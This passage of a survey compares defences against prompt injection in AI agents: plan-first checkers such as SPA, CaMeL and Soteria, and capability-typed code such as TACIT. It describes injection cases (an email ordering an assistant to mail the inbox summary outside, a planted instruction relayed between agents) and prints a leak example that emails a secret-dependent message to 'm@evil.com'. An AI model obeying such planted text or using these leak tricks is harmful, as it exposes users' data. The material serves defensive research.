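A plan covers a single request, whereas a controller like the refund automaton has to cover every case that may come up. In a plan-first agent, the language model writes the whole plan when the request arrives, before it has seen any email, web page or file that a stranger could have written. A checker examines every path through the plan, and an interpreter then carries out exactly what the checker accepted. Planted text that the agent encounters later can't add a step, because the model has already finished planning.

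### Meijer's workflows

The computer scientist Erik Meijer, in *Guardians of the Agents* (2025), traced prompt injection to the missing boundary between instructions and data. In his example, a user asks an assistant to summarize her inbox, and one of the emails tells the assistant to send the summary to an outside address without mentioning it. In Meijer's design, the model writes a workflow in JSON before it reads any email. In shortened form, it looks like this:

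```
fetch_emails:      emails  = fetch_mail()
summarize_emails:  summary = summarize_emails(emails)
return_summary:    return summary
```

The names `emails` and `summary` stand for values that don't exist yet. A language model still does the summarizing, so the planted text may distort the summary, but the workflow has no step that sends mail.

An attacker can also reach the planner earlier, through the description of a third-party tool, and a dishonest user can ask for the extra step directly. Meijer therefore adds a check before the workflow runs. One rule forbids data from flowing from the result of `fetch_mail` to the body of `send_email` if the recipient's address is outside the company. Existing program-analysis tools can search a workflow for such a flow.

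A second example concerns deleting files. The user wants to delete foo.txt and bar.txt, and the tool accepts patterns. The model writes a single step that deletes `*.txt`, because that makes a shorter workflow. Suppose the specification is a postcondition, a statement that must hold when the plan ends:

```
foo.txt does not exist  and  bar.txt does not exist
```

The plan satisfies it but also deletes every other text file. The remedy is a frame condition, which states what must stay the same. Meijer writes one for the tool, requiring that files that don't match the pattern stay unchanged. The request also needs one, requiring that every file except foo.txt and bar.txt remains. The checker then rejects `*.txt` and accepts two separate deletions, because the tool's frame condition guarantees that each deletion leaves the other files unchanged. John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes identified this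 kind of problem in 1969 and named it the frame problem.

The company can write the rule about outside mail once for all requests, but each request needs its own postcondition, and a language model that writes it can forget the frame condition as easily as a person can. Meijer also acknowledged that nobody had formally measured how planning ahead affects an agent's usefulness.

### The six steps of SPA

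Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, did measure it, with a plan language designed for checking. A plan is a JSON list of steps, and each step takes one of six forms:

| Step | What it does |
|---|---|
| retrieve | Loads a result that an earlier request stored |
| tool | Calls a tool; no other step can change anything outside the agent |
| q-llm | Gives text to a quarantined language model, which has no tools and must answer in a declared format |
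| display | Shows something to the user |
| condition | Runs one of two branches |
| loop | Runs the same steps for each item in a collection |

The idea of a quarantined model comes from a 2023 proposal by the programmer Simon Willison, in which one model plans without reading untrusted text and another reads that text but cannot act.

SPA's language has no arithmetic, no text templates and no functions that the planner can define. A condition can compare two values, test whether a collection contains an item, or test whether a value exists. It can't combine tests with "and" or "or", so the planner has to nest one condition inside another. A value created inside a branch disappears when the branch ends. These omissions let the checker determine directly where each argument comes from, because an argument consists only of fixed values and the names of earlier results. With functions and arithmetic,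 the checker would first have to work out what each calculation does. The drawback is that a plan can't compute, for example, half the cost of a kettle, and has to leave that to a tool or to the quarantined model.

Suppose an employee at the shop asks the agent to refund 80 dollars on the order that the customer's latest email is about, provided the customer paid that much. The plan, again in shortened form, could be:

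```
1. email = tool read_latest_email()
2. claim = q-llm("Find the order number", email)
3. order = tool look_up(claim.order)
4. condition order.paid_cents >= 8000:
5.     tool refund(claim.order, 8000)
```

### Labels for secrecy and trust

Before this plan runs, SPA's checker applies information-flow control, which labels data by secrecy or trust and restricts where labelled data may go. Every value gets both labels. A value computed from several others is as secret as the most secret of them and only as trusted as the least trusted. For each tool, the shop sets the highest secrecy it may receive and the lowest trust it requires. A call passes if

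```
secrecy of inputs and context  <=  highest secrecy the tool may receive
trust of inputs and context    >=  lowest trust the tool requires
```

The context covers the decisions that led to the step. Inside a branch, it includes the labels of the values that the condition compared, and inside a loop, it includes the labels of the collection. Without the context, a plan could reveal a secret it never copies, for example by sending an empty email only if a customer's balance is above 1,000 dollars.

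In the refund plan, `email` is untrusted because anyone can write to the shop. `claim` is also untrusted, because passing text through the quarantined model can't make it more trustworthy. The shop allows untrusted input to `look_up`, which changes nothing, but the result is also untrusted, and so is everything inside the condition that depends on that result. The `refund` tool requires trusted input, so the checker rejects the plan before the first step runs.

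The employee wanted exactly these steps. If she had typed the order number herself, the system would have trusted it as part of her request and allowed the same refund.

### What flow control cost on AgentDojo

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo, a standard set of prompt-injection tests that Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2024. It has 97 tasks in four simulated settings: an office workspace, the chat service Slack, a bank and a travel service. It also has 35 attacker goals, and the attacker's instructions appear in tool results. Combining each task with each goal in its setting gives 949 attack runs. Utility is the share of tasks the agent completes, and attack success is the share of attack runs that achieve the attacker's goal.

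With GPT-5.4-nano as the model, SPA produced these results:

| | Utility without attacks | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
| Fixed plan only | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| Fixed plan with flow control | 29.0% | 0.0% |

Only four attacks succeeded against the fixed plan alone, all on one banking task. Planted text passed through the quarantined model into the arguments of sensitive tools, causing three unauthorized transfers and a changed password. Flow control stopped all four attacks, but the agent could no longer complete almost half of the tasks it had been completing.

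That comparison probably understates how much flow control helps. The attacks in this test are instructions, which mostly have no effect on a fixed plan. An attacker who knew about the plan would instead change a value it uses, such as the account number on an invoice.

The checker rejected about 53 per cent of runs when flow control was on, typically because a plan passed one tool's untrusted output to another tool that requires trusted input. A request to pay an invoice fails this way because the account number comes from a document that a stranger wrote. The labels can't distinguish the supplier's real account number from an attacker's. Utility fell by 35 percentage points on the travel tasks, 29 on Slack and 25 on the workspace. It fell by only 6 on banking, but 5 of the 16 banking tasks count as completed even if the agent does nothing.

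Girrens and Wang suggest labelling individual fields instead of whole records and setting a separate requirement for each argument. They also suggest adding an endorsement step, which SPA does not yet have, to raise a value's trust level after an explicit check. For instance, the shop could endorse an order number once ordinary software has confirmed that the order belongs to the customer who sent the email.

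SPA also keeps results for later requests. The planner gets a description of each stored result but not its contents, so an instruction planted in an invoice can't influence a later plan. Each stored result keeps its labels. When Girrens and Wang split the AgentDojo tasks into several requests each, the planner reused an earlier result in 95.4 per cent of the cases where one was available. Hiding the tool descriptions as well, to guard against malicious ones, worked much less well because the planner had to invent the tools it needed, and in about three quarters of runs the software couldn't match them to real ones.

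### CaMeL and restricted Python

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, also separates a planner from a quarantined model, but its plans are programs in a restricted form of Python. As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLoT*, CaMeL's interpreter tags every value with its sources and the people who may read it. When the plan calls a tool, that tool's policy, a Python function, inspects the arguments and their tags and allows or denies the call.

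A policy of this kind can check actual values. For example, it could accept an untrusted order number if the order belongs to the sender, which SPA's labels can't express. But the guarantee depends on many separately written policies, and a plan may fail halfway, after sending its first emails.

Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, report that CaMeL completes 67 per cent of AgentDojo tasks and say that many of the failures occur because it treats all untrusted data as equally risky. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, report that turning on CaMeL's policy checks halves its utility on the banking tasks. These tests used different models from SPA's, so the percentages aren't directly comparable, but flow control substantially reduced utility in both systems.

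Tallam and Miller, who work at a security company, also object to Python as the plan language. Its types are known only when the program runs, errors can jump out of the normal order of steps, and programs can inspect themselves. Even a simple loop can leak:

```
for i in range(secret): fetch("ping")
```

No secret reaches `fetch` as an argument, but anyone who can read the server's log can count the requests. Tallam and Miller recommend a small typed language with bounded loops, secrecy labels built into the types, and no self-inspection.

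Garby and colleagues found a subtler leak. This program is adapted from their example:

```
rich = True
poor = True
if balance > 1000:  poor = False
if poor:            rich = False
if rich:            send_email("m@evil.com", "rich")
```

The program sends the email exactly when the balance is above 1,000. In that case, the interpreter marks `poor` as secret and skips the fourth line. Because the interpreter updates a label only when it runs an assignment, `rich` stays public and the policy allows the email. SPA's language rules out this program because a plan can't reassign an existing name, and nothing created inside a branch can be used after the branch ends.

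The second leak that Garby and colleagues describe is outside the plan. CaMeL retries after a policy blocks a plan, and whether the policy blocked it can reveal one bit of a secret. The retry loop is ordinary, untracked Python, so repeated attempts can extract the whole secret. A planner working on an honest request has little reason to write leaking programs, so both leaks matter most when an attacker can influence the planner, for example through a tool description.

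Garby and colleagues designed a language in which every operation propagates the labels, and proved that its flow guarantee holds for all programs, including those that a model writes during the run. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, their agent completed about as many as CaMeL did without its policy checks, and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

Nikolaou and colleagues kept CaMeL's Python and added a check before the plan runs. Their software, CaMeLoT, turns the plan into a finite automaton and gives it to a model checker. After each pass through a loop, the automaton may repeat the loop or exit, so the check covers any number of repetitions but also rejects some safe plans. One of their rules requires approval before the agent cuts a computer off from the network. CaMeL alone would detect a missing approval only on reaching that step, perhaps after a long and costly analysis. CaMeLoT can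 also enforce a rule that every open ticket must eventually be closed, which a check on single calls can't express naturally.

When a plan fails the check, CaMeLoT describes the counterexample to the planner in English and asks for a repair. SPA ends the request instead, so that nobody can use the checker's answers to adjust a bad plan until it passes. This seems stricter than necessary. No tool has run yet, so the counterexample contains no text from a tool's results. Repeated attempts also can't get a bad plan past a sound check.

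### When one agent instructs another

Many systems now have one agent that delegates work to others. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) showed that CaMeL's protection can fail in such a system even if every agent uses it. A user asked the test system to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. One agent read the applicant database, which contained a planted instruction to email the data to an outsider. A coordinating agent had the text summarized and put the summary into an English request to a messaging agent. The messaging agent treated that request as coming from its user, so its planner read the planted instruction and added the email to its plan.

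Multi-CaMeL extends CaMeL to systems with several agents. It splits each request that one agent sends to another into an instruction, which the receiving planner reads, and a set of variables, which the planner can't read. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. In tests of five models on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded on average in 12.9 per cent of runs without CaMeL, 0.2 per cent with CaMeL in each agent, and none with multi-CaMeL.

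Results varied widely between the models in these averages. Without any defence, 36.1 per cent of the attacks succeeded against GPT-4.1 and none against GPT-5.5. A low attack success rate on AgentDojo is therefore weak evidence for a defence unless the same model does badly without it. Girrens and Wang didn't test their model without a fixed plan, so the case for SPA depends more on how it works than on its attack success rate of zero.

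Peters-Gill and colleagues switched off all data policies, so their results measure the effect of planning ahead by itself. On a set of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL lowered the success rate by 21.6 points on average, but by 13.4 for the two strongest models. Multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2 points on average and by less than one point for those two. The researchers also had to add a description of every tool's output format, because the planner has to specify how to parse results it never sees.

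### Soteria

He, Desai and colleagues (2026), in *SOTERIA*, use plans to enforce business rules. A Soteria plan consists of named states, with at most one action on each transition between them. This one, slightly simplified, cancels a flight reservation:

```
LOOKUP:     resv  = get_reservation(id)        go to CHECK_AGE
CHECK_AGE:  hours = hours_since(resv.booked)   go to DECIDE
DECIDE:     if hours <= 24 go to CANCEL, otherwise go to REFUSE
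CANCEL:     cancel(id)                         go to DONE
```

The plan looks reasonable, but the airline also requires a check that the customer hasn't already flown part of the trip. Since `hours` can be any number, the checker can't visit every state one by one as it would for a finite automaton. It carries a formula from state to state that sums up what must be true there. At CANCEL, the formula contains what the two earlier tools promise about their results, plus `hours <= 24`. An automated program verifier called Dafny then has to prove three things:

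- Every call meets the conditions its tool places on inputs.
- The plan can't get stuck, because in every state at least one way forward is open.
- Every path obeys the policy.

To check the plan against the policy, the checker adds an imaginary log of the plan's calls. The airline's rule requires every cancellation in this log to have an earlier flown-status check on the same reservation that returned "true". On the path through CANCEL, the log contains a cancellation but no such check, so the proof fails and the planner gets an error message identifying the broken rule. Plans may not contain cycles. Dafny verifies common procedures once as sub-plans, and larger plans can then rely on their stated inputs and results. With sub-plans, 65 of 68 plans passed within eight retries, compared with 38 of 60 without them.

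In Soteria's normal mode, a language model carries out the task with the plan as a guide. The model may depart from the plan, so a monitor checks each call against the same rules. On 50 airline tasks, verifying the plans without this monitor reduced violations only from 13 to 10 with GPT-5.4-mini and from 27 to 24 with Gemini 3 Flash. Adding the monitor reduced both to zero. A proof about a plan protects little if the agent can do something else, and for high-stakes work Soteria has a strict mode that permits only the plan's own steps.

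Soteria had no rule violations across 207 tasks and four models, largely because its monitor enforces the same 98 rules that the test checks. The gain in completed tasks is more informative. With Soteria, Claude Opus 4.6 completed 88.0 per cent of the airline tasks without breaking a rule, compared with 56.0 per cent with the best alternative. On the retail tasks, the figures were 90.4 and 46.5 per cent. Agents without a plan often collected all the information they needed and then handed the customer to a human.

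Other results were less favourable. On a set of file, terminal and document tasks, Opus completed 18.6 per cent with Soteria and 30.2 per cent without any safeguard, though it broke rules in more than half of the tasks it completed without one. Soteria raised the cost of an airline task from 32 to 80 cents, because its planner writes a new plan after each customer message. When He and colleagues allowed only three retries, GPT-5.4-mini averaged 50.8 per cent on the airline tasks, close to the 48.0 per cent it reached with AgentSpec's rules.

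One agent without safeguards exploited a loophole by upgrading a reservation to business class, which customers may cancel, and then cancelling it. He and colleagues say the airline's policy doesn't permit this. But their two formal cancellation rules would accept the cancellation if the agent looked the reservation up again after the upgrade and confirmed that the customer hadn't flown. As with `*.txt`, the rules omit something their authors took for granted.

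### PDDL and plan validators

Researchers in automated planning have had a common language for such problems since 1998, the Planning Domain Definition Language, or PDDL. A PDDL problem lists the objects, the facts that hold at the start, the possible actions and the goal. Each action has preconditions, which must hold before it, and effects, which it makes true or false. The shop's refund could look like this:

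```
(:action refund
  :parameters   (?o - order)
  :precondition (and (looked_up ?o) (paid ?o)
                     (not (refunded ?o)))
  :effect       (refunded ?o))
```

A plan is then a list of actions, such as `look_up(4417)`, `refund(4417)`, `send_receipt(4417)`. A program called a validator checks it by simulation:

1. It starts with the facts that hold at the beginning.
2. For each action in turn, it tests the preconditions and rejects the plan if one fails.
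3. It applies the action's effects to the facts.
4. After the last action, it accepts the plan if the goal holds.

If the plan tries to refund order 4417 twice, the second refund fails because `refunded` is already true. Validating a plan takes a single pass, whether a planning program, a language model or a person wrote it. The plan also uses the action names directly, which avoids the translation from English that sometimes lost a plan's intent in the tests by Ramani and colleagues.

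An action in PDDL changes only the facts listed in its effects, so each action has its frame condition built in. The goal has no built-in frame condition, so if it mentions only foo.txt and bar.txt, a plan that also deletes other files passes. To exclude such plans, the goal has to list the files to keep.

Basic PDDL describes the world with true-or-false facts, and later versions add numbers and durations. He et al. note that it lacks the richer data types their plans use, such as whole reservation records. A classical plan is a fixed list of actions, which assumes the starting facts are known and every action works as described. It can't include a step such as "if the warehouse has a spare kettle, send it, and otherwise give a refund".

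### When the next step depends on what the agent finds

Branches cover the alternatives that the planner can foresee. A stranger can still influence which branch the agent takes. A false claim in an email can lead the agent into the refund branch, although it can't add a new branch to the plan. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this branch steering. SPA prevents it for sensitive tools by treating everything inside a branch that can be steered this way as untrusted, which is one reason it rejects so many legitimate plans.

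Loops cover an unknown number of items, such as all orders that are more than a week late. SPA's checker needs to examine the steps inside a loop only once, because their labels don't depend on how often they run. The total amount does depend on how often they run, so the shop still has to enforce its daily limit while the plan runs.

If a step needs judgement, a Soteria plan can leave the choice to a language model and attach a condition to the answer. In one example, the model picks flights for a group, and the software checks that it picked at least one flight and that each has enough seats.

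Sometimes a result calls for an action that nobody foresaw. In tests by Peters-Gill and colleagues, most of the failures of CaMeL and multi-CaMeL happened because the agent had committed to a plan before seeing the data. In several cases, an agent asked another for data from one period, received data from a nearby period, and carried on because its plan had no step for noticing the difference.

An agent can plan again after reading new data, but a planner that reads the data can also read an instruction planted in it. Soteria allows replanning despite this risk and relies on its rules to limit the damage. In *ActGuard* (2026), the agent plans only one step ahead. With each action, it predicts which tools it might use next, before it sees the action's result. If it then chooses a different tool, an audit takes the mismatch into account. The agent isn't restricted to the tools it predicted,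 so it stays flexible, but the method offers no guarantee. Dantas and colleagues found no study in their survey that gives a guarantee before the run for plans that an agent assembles as it goes. They suggest verifying templates with blanks in advance, then checking that each new plan fills in a verified template.

A template wouldn't help with a request to follow the instructions on a supplier's return form, since the form determines the steps. The shop can instead use two plans. The first only reads the form and shows it to an employee. She then requests the steps she agrees with, so the second plan is based on a trusted request.

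## Code whose types limit what it can touch

An agent can also write ordinary programs, with functions, loops and recursion, while a type checker limits what they may do. The checker works out which files, network connections and tools each part of a program could use, and rejects the program if any part could use something it shouldn't. It doesn't predict the program's results, which no algorithm can do for every program.

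*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) presents TACIT, which does this for Scala 3, a general-purpose language. TACIT runs as an MCP server, so existing agents such as Claude Code can connect to it. The agent sends Scala code, and TACIT runs it only if the Scala compiler accepts it. The user has to switch off the agent's built-in tools for files, commands and the web, because they would bypass this check.

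### Capabilities and capture sets

A capability is a value that a program must hold to use a resource. In most languages, any line of code can open a file by giving its name. In a language with object capabilities, the code needs an object that stands for the file, and it can get one only from code that already has access. An agent can't make up such an object the way it can make up a file name. Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn proposed capabilities in 1966, and several operating systems have used them since.

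Scala 3 has an experimental feature called capture checking, which records capabilities in types. Suppose `f` is a capability for a file. This function takes a piece of text and writes it to the file:

```
(s: String) => f.write(s)
```

A function of type `String ->{f} Unit` takes a string, returns no useful result and may use the capability `f`. The names in braces are its capture set. A function of type `String -> Unit`, without braces, has an empty capture set and is called pure. It can't write to a file, send a request or print anything, because it holds no capabilities.

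A capture set includes everything a function could use, but it may also include things the function never uses. If a function mentions `f` only in a branch that never runs, the set still includes `f`. The check is therefore sound but incomplete. In return, the compiler can check each function separately, using only the types of the functions it calls. Without such types, a precise analysis would have to trace which function each variable might hold, and Odersky and colleagues note that this can take exponential time.

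Capture sets also prevent code from keeping a capability for later. In TACIT, the agent requests access to a folder for the duration of one block of code. The compiler accepts this program, which reads a customer's claim:

```
val claim = requestFileSystem("/shop/claims") {
  val f = access("4417.txt")
  f.read()
}
```

Here `requestFileSystem` creates a capability for the folder, and `access` uses it to produce `f`, a capability for one file. The block returns the file's text, which is allowed because a string holds no capabilities. The types don't show whether a path lies inside the folder, so TACIT checks that while the program runs.

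The compiler rejects the program after a small change to the last line of the block:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("/shop/claims") {
  val f = access("4417.txt")
  () => f.read()
}
```

The block now returns a function of type `() ->{f} String`, which would read the file whenever the program called it. But `f` exists only inside the block, so the type of `later` can't include `f`. The compiler reports that the capability would escape, and the program never starts. An agent that had permission to read claims in one step therefore can't carry that permission into the next.

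### What safe mode removes

Full Scala lets programmers override the type checker when they know better. Scala's *Safe Mode*, a page of the language's documentation, sets out six restrictions for code that nobody has reviewed, such as an agent's:

- No unchecked casts or pattern matches. A cast tells the compiler to treat a value as having another type. An agent could use one to relabel a function that writes to a file as pure.
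- No features from the module `caps.unsafe`, which can exempt a variable from capability tracking.
- No `@unchecked` annotations, which switch off individual compiler checks.
- No reflection, which looks up functions by name while the program runs, when the compiler can no longer see which ones it uses.
- No compiling without capture checking, which must also cover changes to variables. Otherwise a supposedly pure function could copy a secret into an outside variable, and other code could send it.
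- No global library code unless it is safe too. An ordinary library function might open a network connection without requiring a capability.

Some harmless library code breaks these rules, such as a cache, which has to change a hidden variable. A developer can mark such a module `@assumeSafe` after checking it by hand or proving it correct, and the agent may then use it. The same annotation allows a mail function that prompts the user for confirmation before sending anything.

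Safe mode does allow exceptions, the errors that interrupt a program, although they can leak information. For example, a function that fails only when a card number starts with 4 would reveal whether it does. Many ordinary operations can fail, too many for the compiler to track, so TACIT catches exceptions at run time and turns them into values it can keep secret.

At first, TACIT didn't use the compiler's safe mode. According to the project's GitHub page, lampepfl's *TACIT*, a validator instead searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns, a check that is easier to evade. Glama's *TACIT*, a copy of a later version of the page, lists safe mode as on by default.

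The theory behind capture checking is better established. *What's in the Box* (2025) proves that a small core version of it is sound, and the proof assistant Lean has checked every step. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) extends the Lean proofs to rules about kinds of capability, and *System Capybara* (2026) proves similar guarantees for a core language that tracks changes to data. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode still needs a proof.

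### Secrets that the model can't read

Limiting access to resources doesn't prevent leaks that combine two permitted actions, such as reading a confidential complaint and sending text to the company that hosts the agent's language model. TACIT therefore wraps secret data in a type called `Classified`. Its `map` function applies a calculation to the hidden value and wraps the result again, but it accepts only pure functions:

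```
val doc   = readClassified("complaint.txt")
val start = doc.map(text => text.take(200))
doc.map(text => outbox.write(text))
```

The compiler accepts the second line, which keeps the first 200 characters of the complaint. It rejects the third line because the function there has `outbox` in its capture set.

The agent can process the complaint this way without seeing it. For work that needs language skills, TACIT provides a second model that runs locally and is trusted by the user. This model can read and summarize the complaint, but its summary comes back wrapped in `Classified`.

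The user still needs to see the summary, so TACIT has two output channels. When the agent's code prints a classified value, the agent's channel shows only `Classified(****)`, while a secure channel shows the user the real text. If the user asks for the summary's length, the agent can write code that counts the characters, and again only the user sees the number. CaMeL's labels, by contrast, are lost once a value enters the model's conversation as plain language.

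### Leaks and task performance

Odersky and colleagues tested this protection on a software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with 10 planted instructions, some of which included ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets. Another 11 prompts were direct requests for secrets or were written as if from someone entitled to them, such as an administrator. This gave each model 131 trials with classified types and 131 without. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

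With classified types, neither model leaked a secret. Without them, 98.5 per cent of trials were secure with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 91.6 per cent with MiniMax M2.5. Sonnet followed none of the 120 planted instructions but did follow two of the malicious prompts. MiniMax followed three planted instructions and eight malicious prompts. The perfect score with classified types follows from the design, which never gives the model the secrets, so the trials mainly test whether TACIT implements that design correctly.

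The protection didn't reduce the number of ordinary tasks the agents completed. Sonnet completed 99.2 per cent with classified types and 83.3 per cent without them, while MiniMax completed 90.0 per cent with them and 88.3 per cent without. Sonnet's gap may be an artefact, because without protection it often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

A separate experiment tested whether agents perform worse when they write typed Scala. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, three models handled airline and retail tasks ten times each. All three scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with Scala than with ordinary tool calls. Odersky and colleagues attribute the improvement to the typed results and the compiler's error messages. Between 0.32 and 7.93 per cent of the snippets needed a retry, usually only one, often because the model had overlooked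 a possible null value or mistyped a dollar sign.

On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems, MiniMax solved 41.7 per cent with TACIT and 43.3 per cent with its usual tools. The difference is five problems, too small to be strong evidence that either setup is better.

### Why it cost less than flow control on plans

SPA's flow control made an agent fail almost half of the AgentDojo tasks it had previously completed, whereas TACIT barely reduced task completion on τ²-bench. The difference arises partly because τ²-bench gave the agent customer records and reservations as ordinary values, so there were no secrets for the compiler to protect and few grounds for rejecting a program.

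AgentDojo is a harder test, because most emails, files and web pages in the TACIT version are classified. TACIT completed between 40 and 69 per cent of tasks, depending on the setting and the model. With OpenAI's o4-mini-high, it did worse than CaMeL's published results in all four settings, and on office tasks it completed 53 per cent compared with CaMeL's 81 per cent. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, it did better than CaMeL on banking and travel and worse in the other two settings.

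Only one of about 1,900 attacks on the TACIT agent succeeded. In that attack, a user asked the agent to book a hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and AgentDojo counted the mention of the other hotel as a successful attack. TACIT's rules allowed the agent to show public reviews to the user, so Odersky and colleagues blame the scoring method.

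SPA's checker rejected the refund plan because the order number came from a customer's email. TACIT allows the same refund only if the shop leaves the email unclassified. The agent can then read the email as an ordinary string, find the order number and call `refund`. If the shop classifies the email, the agent can obtain only a classified order number, which `refund` doesn't accept, so the task fails. The consultancy VirtusLab warns that classifying too much data would greatly reduce an agent's usefulness.

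TACIT also leaves the agent more room to adapt. The agent writes one short program, reads any unclassified results and then writes the next, so it doesn't have to foresee every case. If the compiler rejects a program, the agent gets the error message and, unlike in SPA, can try again.

Because of this freedom, planted text in an unclassified email can still influence the agent's next program. That program may refund the wrong order, and the types will allow it if the agent holds the capability for refunds. The later TACIT documentation states that classification protects "confidentiality, not integrity". Unless the user changes a setting, an agent can even overwrite a classified file that it can't read, such as the list of keys that allow login to a computer.

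### What the types do not cover

Like a valid tool call, a well-typed program can still do the wrong thing, and its timing can leak secrets. A pure function could run a long calculation if the first digit of a card number is odd, and the delay would reveal one bit. Capture checking doesn't track how long code takes or whether it finishes. Garby and colleagues' proof for labels tracked at run time also doesn't cover leaks through whether a program finishes.

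The types also don't control external commands once they start. TACIT lets an agent run only commands on a list, but a listed command may do more than its name suggests. Odersky and colleagues give `sbt`, a tool for building Scala projects, as an example of a safe command, but `sbt` runs code from the project's files, which the agent may be able to edit. They recommend a sandbox as a second layer of protection.

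The guarantee depends on library code that developers marked as safe by hand. TACIT's reusable part is about 1,000 lines long, and each new set of tools needs a few hundred more. If a developer forgets to classify the result of one function, the compiler cannot detect the mistake.

### LACUNA

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) describes a later, more ambitious system from the same laboratory. A developer leaves a gap in a program, such as `agent[Int]("count the late orders")`, and a language model fills it with code while the program runs. The compiler checks the new code as if the developer had typed it there, so the code can use only the variables and tools available at that point.

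The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. Suppose the model writes code that subtracts 50 from a balance and then returns text where the program needs a number. The compiler rejects both steps, so the balance doesn't change. In Python, the subtraction would happen before the error appeared.

LACUNA's results suggest that typed code can reduce performance more than the TACIT experiments indicated. On 392 τ²-bench tasks, DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0 per cent with LACUNA and 90.0 per cent with ordinary tool calls, although Zhao and colleagues call these results "on par". The compiler rejected 8.6 per cent of the model's code on a web research test and 22.4 per cent on the retail tasks. For a weaker Gemini model, the rejection rate reached 89 per cent on telecoms tasks. The effect evidently depends on how well a model writes Scala, which is probably much rarer in training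 data than Python.

Eight of about 1,900 AgentDojo attacks succeeded against LACUNA. Zhao and colleagues explain that the types can't stop an attacker from getting the model to misuse a capability the task requires. Developers therefore have to give each piece of code as few capabilities as possible.

### Other languages that could serve

Scala isn't the only possible host. Odersky and colleagues say that a language needs capabilities that nobody can forge, control over every effect that matters for safety, and a way to mark parts of a program as pure. They compare several candidates:

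| Language | What it offers | What it lacks |
|---|---|---|
| Scala 3 | Capabilities in types, pure functions | A finished version of capture checking |
| Haskell | Types that separate pure code from code with effects | Built-in capabilities |
| E and Joe-E | Capabilities enforced at run time | Types that show which capabilities a function holds |
| Other mainstream languages | Existing tools and users | Capability tracking and guaranteed purity |
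| A new small language | A type system designed for agents | Human readers, tools and examples to learn from |

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) presents ELBA, a Haskell system in which an agent's program must have a type that permits only certain effects. ELBA relies on a restricted form of Haskell that, according to GHC's *Safe Haskell* documentation, removes the loopholes that let code get around its types. Haskell has no built-in capabilities, so ELBA's library supplies them. For example, an agent can open a file only through a `Path` value, which it can narrow to a subfolder but can't create from a string.

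ELBA can also control where data comes from. In one example, an agent may add entries to a bibliography only if they come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that writes an entry accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`, which only the function that fetches entries from DBLP can create. Similarly, the shop's `refund` function could accept only an order that a look-up function has matched to the customer. The agent could then act on an order number from an email without being able to refund another customer's order. Zhou and colleagues report that ELBA completed more AgentDojo tasks than CaMeL across a range of models and attacks.

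Many coding agents work through shell commands, which no such type system covers. *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) presents CapScope, a system for these agents that keeps the capabilities outside the language and checks them at each tool call. CapScope sets the limits from the user's request and the project's file names before the agent reads any file. It then gives each sub-agent only the permissions its job needs. A sub-agent that runs tests, for example, can't edit source code, even if the test output contains an instruction to do so.

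Planted instructions took effect in 3 of 75 runs with CapScope, compared with 33 to 47 of 75 under three less strict arrangements. The agents completed 68 of 75 repairs with CapScope and 68 to 72 without it. But CapScope doesn't track data, so unlike `Classified`, it can't keep secrets from leaking.

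## MISRA C and SPARK as restricted programming languages

Makers of cars, aircraft and medical devices restricted programming languages long before anyone needed to check an AI's code. They use language subsets, which are general-purpose languages with the hard-to-check features removed. MISRA C is a set of rules for using C, the most common language for the small computers inside machines. SPARK is a cut-down version of Ada, designed so that software can prove properties of programs written in it. Programs in either can run to many thousands of lines, which leaves far more to check than in a tool call or a plan.

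### What goes wrong in C

C gives programmers direct access to the hardware and doesn't check for errors while a program runs. Bagnara, Bagnara and Hill (2018), in *The MISRA C Coding Standard and its Role in the Development*, explain that the C standard also leaves many operations undefined, because this makes it easier to write fast compilers for almost any processor. An undefined operation may have any result at all. For example:

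```
uint32_t x = 1;
x = x << 32;
```

The second line shifts a 32-bit number 32 places to the left, which should push out its only 1 and leave 0. But many Intel processors use only the last five binary digits of the shift distance. For 32 these are all 0, so the processor doesn't shift anything and x stays 1. A checker that assumed either result could be wrong about the program that runs. MISRA C bans such shifts.

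### From the 1994 guidelines to MISRA C:2025

MISRA, originally short for Motor Industry Software Reliability Association, began in 1990 as part of a British government programme. In November 1994 it published guidelines for vehicle software that advised manufacturers to consider a restricted subset of a programming language. Ford and Land Rover were then each writing their own rules for C. According to MISRA's *Frequently asked questions*, they agreed that a joint publication would be more useful to the industry, and the first edition of MISRA C followed in 1998. Railway, aerospace and medical companies later adopted it too.

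The current edition, MISRA C:2025, appeared in March 2025. SciTools' *MISRA C 2025* lists 223 guidelines. Of these, 201 are rules, which concern only the source code, and 22 are directives, which also depend on other information, such as whether each piece of code serves a documented requirement. Every guideline belongs to a category:

- **Mandatory:** the code must never break it.
- **Required:** the code may break it only with a formal deviation.
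- **Advisory:** programmers should follow it as far as is practical.

A deviation is a written exception that names the guideline, describes where and why the code breaks it, and sets out precautions. A designated expert must approve it. MISRA (2020) rules out the programmer's convenience as a reason, but accepts the need to access hardware that standard C can't address. A project may make a guideline stricter, for example by treating a required rule as mandatory, but it can't downgrade a required guideline.

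Bagnara and Hill (2021) stress in *A Rationale-Based Classification* that MISRA C is meant to prevent errors rather than find them, so it bans kinds of code that often cause errors, even where a particular use is harmless.

### Decidable and undecidable rules

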